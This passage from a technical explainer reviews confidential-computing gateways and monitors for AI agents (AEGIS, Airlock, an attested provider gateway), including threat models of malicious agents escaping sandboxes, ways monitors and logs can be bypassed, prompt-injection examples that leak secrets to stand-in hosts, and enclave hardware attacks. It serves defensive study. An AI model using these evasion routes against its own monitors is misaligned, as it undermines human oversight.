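Customers have to review 851 lines of the relay's code. To test whether coding agents could do this review, the researchers planted ten flaws. Codex found eight, Claude Code found all ten, and neither reported a problem in the clean version. But these were separate flaws planted in a small program. A dishonest operator would try to hide a flaw, and might test it against the same coding agents before publishing the code.

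There is also a mathematical proof of confidentiality. In it, the host chooses two conversations that look the same from outside, the enclave relays one of them at random, and the host guesses which. The host's advantage is the difference between its chance of guessing correctly and 50%. Xie and colleagues prove that this is at most the sum of an attacker's advantages at five other tasks:

- reading the enclave's memory
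- making its program misbehave
- forging an attestation
- breaking the encrypted connection from the client
- breaking the encrypted connection to the provider

All five are negligible if the hardware and the encryption are sound. The proof also assumes that the relay's own code doesn't leak the conversation. Xie and colleagues support this assumption with the code review, tests of the relay and a computer-checked model of the protocol, but they leave a full proof for future work.

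### What the host still learns

The host sees the length and timing of every request and reply, which account and provider handled each request, whether it succeeded, and how many tokens it used. The host also sees the gateway key.

Providers send replies in small pieces, and the size of each encrypted piece can reveal the length of the next token. Xie and colleagues cite earlier research that reconstructed text from sequences of these lengths. A gateway operator is well placed to do this, because it can send its own prompts through the same accounts and learn which texts produce which sizes. Ordinary prose is probably more exposed than a random API key, since the method depends on guessing likely words. The enclave could pad every piece to the same size, but the prototype doesn't.

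AEGIS assumes that the provider is honest and that nobody attacks the hardware physically or through side channels (indirect signs of a computation, such as its timing, that can reveal secrets). The host can always stop the service.

AEGIS relays conversations without screening them. If a malicious web page leads the model to propose a command that sends Tiger-winter-58 to notes.example, AEGIS delivers the command intact. AEGIS protects customers from the gateway's operator, so a company that also wants to restrict its agents needs a different monitor.

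### Airlock: a monitor in its own virtual machine

In *Airlock*, Abdollahi, Al Sadi and colleagues (2026) describe a monitor that does enforce rules. They assume the agent may be malicious and may take over the operating system it runs on, with help from a malicious host. They cite an OpenAI report of agents escaping several kinds of sandbox during training.

Airlock runs each agent in one confidential virtual machine (VM) and its monitor in another, called the Airlock VM. The agent's VM has no direct access to a network or disk. Trusted firmware, the low-level software underneath both machines, lets the agent's VM exchange data only with the Airlock VM.

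When build-7 contacts GitHub, the Airlock VM checks the destination and the HTTP method against the user's policy. If the policy allows both, the VM opens the connection and replaces the agent's fake token with the real one. The Airlock VM is therefore a credential broker, and it has to read the request to insert the token. It also checks every file access, so an agent couldn't get around a refusal by using the shell, as in the tests by Li and colleagues.

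Each agent has its own Airlock VM, so in the earlier example of forty agents, a break-in to one VM would expose three credentials instead of 120. As with one broker per team, this separation helps less if the agents share credentials or if one flaw lets an attacker into every Airlock VM.

Airlock doesn't examine what a permitted request means. If the policy lets build-7 post comments on GitHub, a malicious web page could still get it to post a customer's record there.

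### Two guarantees for when Airlock fails

Abdollahi and colleagues plan for the possibility that the agent reaches the network without going through the Airlock VM. The agent would have only fake credentials, so it couldn't log in to anything with them, but it could still send out any file or customer record it had already read.

If an attacker takes over the Airlock VM, the records from before the break-in remain trustworthy. The Airlock VM sends its log to Azure Confidential Ledger, an append-only log run by Microsoft:

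1. The Airlock VM records each network connection and file operation. It combines repeated reads and writes of an open file into one record.
2. Each record includes a hash of the previous one, so removing or changing a record breaks the chain.
3. The Airlock VM groups the records, by default every two seconds, and sends each group to the ledger with a hash that covers all of it.
4. The ledger returns a signed receipt.

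A new HTTPS connection has to wait until the ledger has its record, so an attacker can't open one and then erase the evidence. File accesses don't wait, so an attacker could hide the last few seconds of them. The attacker can also add false records after the break-in. If a group has more records than fit in a ledger entry, the ledger keeps only the hash and a count for the rest, so an attacker can destroy their contents by deleting the local copies.

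The first record in the chain is the Airlock VM's attestation, which identifies the key used to write the log. An investigator can therefore check which software produced the records and which policy was in force. This check would have been useful after the October attack on LiteLLM, when the attacker deleted records of the build process.

A log that nobody can delete should contain as little as possible. Airlock mostly records destinations and file names, but these can contain secrets too. If build-7 tried to contact tiger-winter-58.attacker.example, the ledger could permanently record the password in that address, and the company would have to change the password. The log also has limited detail, showing that build-7 connected to GitHub but not what it did there.

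An attacker who takes over the Airlock VM still gets the agent's credentials and can ignore the policy from then on. Stored files need separate protection because the processor protects only memory. Abdollahi and colleagues have tried adding an encrypted file system that detects when someone restores an old version of the disk.

### What Airlock costs

Abdollahi and colleagues ran 12 agent tasks six times each. The average task took 85.7 seconds with both parts in one virtual machine, 91.4 seconds with Airlock, and 95.0 seconds with Airlock and the external ledger, a total increase of 11%. Most of the time went to waiting for the model. In local processing alone, Airlock without the ledger was 33% slower.

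The ledger delayed each new HTTPS connection by about 0.26 seconds, and the average task opened 14.6 such connections. The maximum speed of data transfer between the agent and its monitor fell by 51% to 70%, which would matter more for an agent that downloads large files. The Airlock VM also used one of the three processor cores and a third of the memory, and each agent would need its own monitor.

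These figures are estimates because no commercial processor yet had the Arm security features that Airlock needs, so the researchers imitated them in software on a small development board. They expect real hardware to be faster. They tested only speed and whether the parts worked together, which provides little evidence about how well Airlock would resist a determined agent.

### A gateway that chooses the provider inside the enclave

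In *Evidence-Bound Gateway-Path Provenance for Third-Party LLM Inference*, Wang and Tian (2026) divide a gateway similarly to AEGIS but move more of its work into the enclave. The outer part, which they call the business plane, checks logins and quotas, forwards encrypted messages and stores records. The enclave chooses the provider, writes the request and calculates the price.

The customer sends the enclave a contract that specifies which providers it may use and when. For example, the contract may require the enclave to try provider A first and use provider B only if A fails to answer in time. The operator has its own policy, and the enclave does only what both allow. Afterwards, it signs a receipt listing the providers it tried, the token count, the expected charge and a hash of the reply. A gateway therefore can't secretly go straight to a cheaper provider or charge for tokens that the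 provider never reported. However, the enclave can't verify that the provider ran the model it advertises.

This design also removes the weakness in AEGIS's key storage. The owner of a provider key verifies the enclave and encrypts the key so that only the enclave can read it. The enclave keeps the key only in memory, so the owner must send it again after a restart.

| System | What someone who takes over the host gets | What someone who takes over the enclave's program gets |
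|---|---|---|
| AEGIS | Provider keys, gateway keys, lengths and timing | Conversations, and the keys sent with them |
| Wang and Tian's gateway | Customers' logins, receipts, lengths and timing | Conversations and all the provider keys it holds |
| Airlock | Some timing, and stored files unless the disk has its own protection | One agent's traffic, files and credentials |

The receipts create a smaller leak, because the host stores them and they contain an unkeyed hash of the request. Someone who knows all of a request except a nine-digit number could try every possible number until the hash matched. Wang and Tian acknowledge that such a hash can confirm a guess.

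The added delay was about 0.4 milliseconds, but this was measured on a single Apple computer without an enclave. On Amazon's enclaves, all 30 requests to a real provider succeeded. Each request used only one approved provider, so the rules for switching between providers have worked only in tests with simulated providers.

### Attested code can still be dangerous

An attestation shows which program is running, but the program may have flaws or be malicious. LiteLLM's SQL injection would have worked just as well inside an enclave, because the proxy's code mishandled the attacker's request. The malicious release in October came from LiteLLM's own build process with valid signatures, and an enclave running it would have produced a valid attestation.

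AEGIS depends on customers to review the code before they accept its measurement. Customers who don't want to review every version can instead accept any measurement signed by a key they trust. But an attacker who controlled the release process, as in October, could get malware signed with that key.

A monitor that does more is harder to review. Xie and colleagues compared AEGIS with another open-source enclave gateway, which also chooses providers, changes requests and handles payments. Counted the same way, AEGIS had 1,236 lines of code and the other gateway had 10,434. Airlock adds more than 9,000 lines to its firmware and monitor, and depends on a complete Linux kernel. The AEGIS count leaves out the shared software underneath the relay, so the real difference between AEGIS and Airlock is smaller than these numbers suggest.

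A monitor that judges the meaning of a conversation would need far more trusted code, perhaps including a language model. Hardware can already protect such a model. *Benchmarking Confidential Computing Performance on NVIDIA Blackwell GPUs* (2026) describes how Nvidia's confidential mode extends the protection to the graphics processors that run models, so the host can't read the prompts or generated text. But no customer can review a language model line by line, and an agent's conversation could contain instructions meant to mislead the model.

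Matching exact secrets needs much less code. A relay like AEGIS could search conversations for hashed secrets, as described earlier, and keep the hash key inside the enclave. None of the three systems includes such a check. Anyone adding one would have to limit what it reports to the host, because reporting every match would reveal which conversations contain secrets.

If the monitor's rules change often and are part of its program, customers have to check a new measurement after every change. Wang and Tian avoid this by sending the contract to the enclave separately, and Airlock does the same with its policies. The measurement then no longer identifies the rules the monitor follows, so both systems have to record them in signed receipts or in the external log.

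### Attacks on enclave hardware

All three systems assume that the hardware is sound, but researchers have repeatedly found ways to break it. In October 2025, The Hacker News (2025) reported on TEE.fail, an attack that uses a device costing under $1,000 to watch the data passing between a server's processor and its memory. The data is encrypted, but SC Media explains that the chips use deterministic encryption, which encrypts the same value in the same place identically every time. The researchers could use the repeated patterns to extract secret keys from Intel and AMD systems, in some cases including the keys that sign attestations. BlindBox uses a counter to prevent this kind of repetition.

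Such a key would defeat AEGIS's checks on any platform it covers. An attacker could run an ordinary program that copies every conversation, and use the key to sign a document stating that the program is the approved relay. The sidecar would accept the document and send the password. According to SecurityWeek, stolen attestation keys can also be used against Nvidia's confidential mode, so a monitor that runs a language model would have the same problem. SC Media reports that neither Intel nor AMD planned to issue a fix.

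TEE.fail requires physical access to the server. *Two-Way Confidential VMs (2cVM)* (2026) describes Battering RAM, another attack that uses a device attached to the memory. Battering RAM can bypass AMD's attestation by replaying memory from a different virtual machine.

In *Insecure Despite Proven Updated*, Shen and Qin (2026) attacked AMD's EPYC Milan processors, the first generation with this type of protection, without physical access. Each chip contains a secret seed, which it hashes repeatedly to make the signing key for a given firmware version, with more repetitions for older versions. Someone who breaks into version 10 can continue hashing to get the keys for versions 9 and 8, but can't go back to version 11. Shen and Qin broke into old firmware and then extracted the seed itself, which gives the keys for every version. An attacker with full control of the host who can replace its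 firmware could therefore forge an attestation for any version, including the latest.

None of these attacks targeted Amazon's Nitro Enclaves, which AEGIS uses. A gateway operator who rents an enclave from Amazon can't attach a device to the server, so the customer mostly has to trust Amazon. An operator with its own servers could attach one easily. Customers should therefore ask who has physical access to the machine. They should also refuse attestations from processors with known flaws. To defend against physical attacks, *TEE Anchor* (2026) proposes that organisations vouch for particular machines.

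A company that later learns of a flaw can stop sending new conversations, but it can't take back the secrets it has already sent. It would have to replace every password and key that passed through the affected enclave, as it would after using a dishonest gateway.
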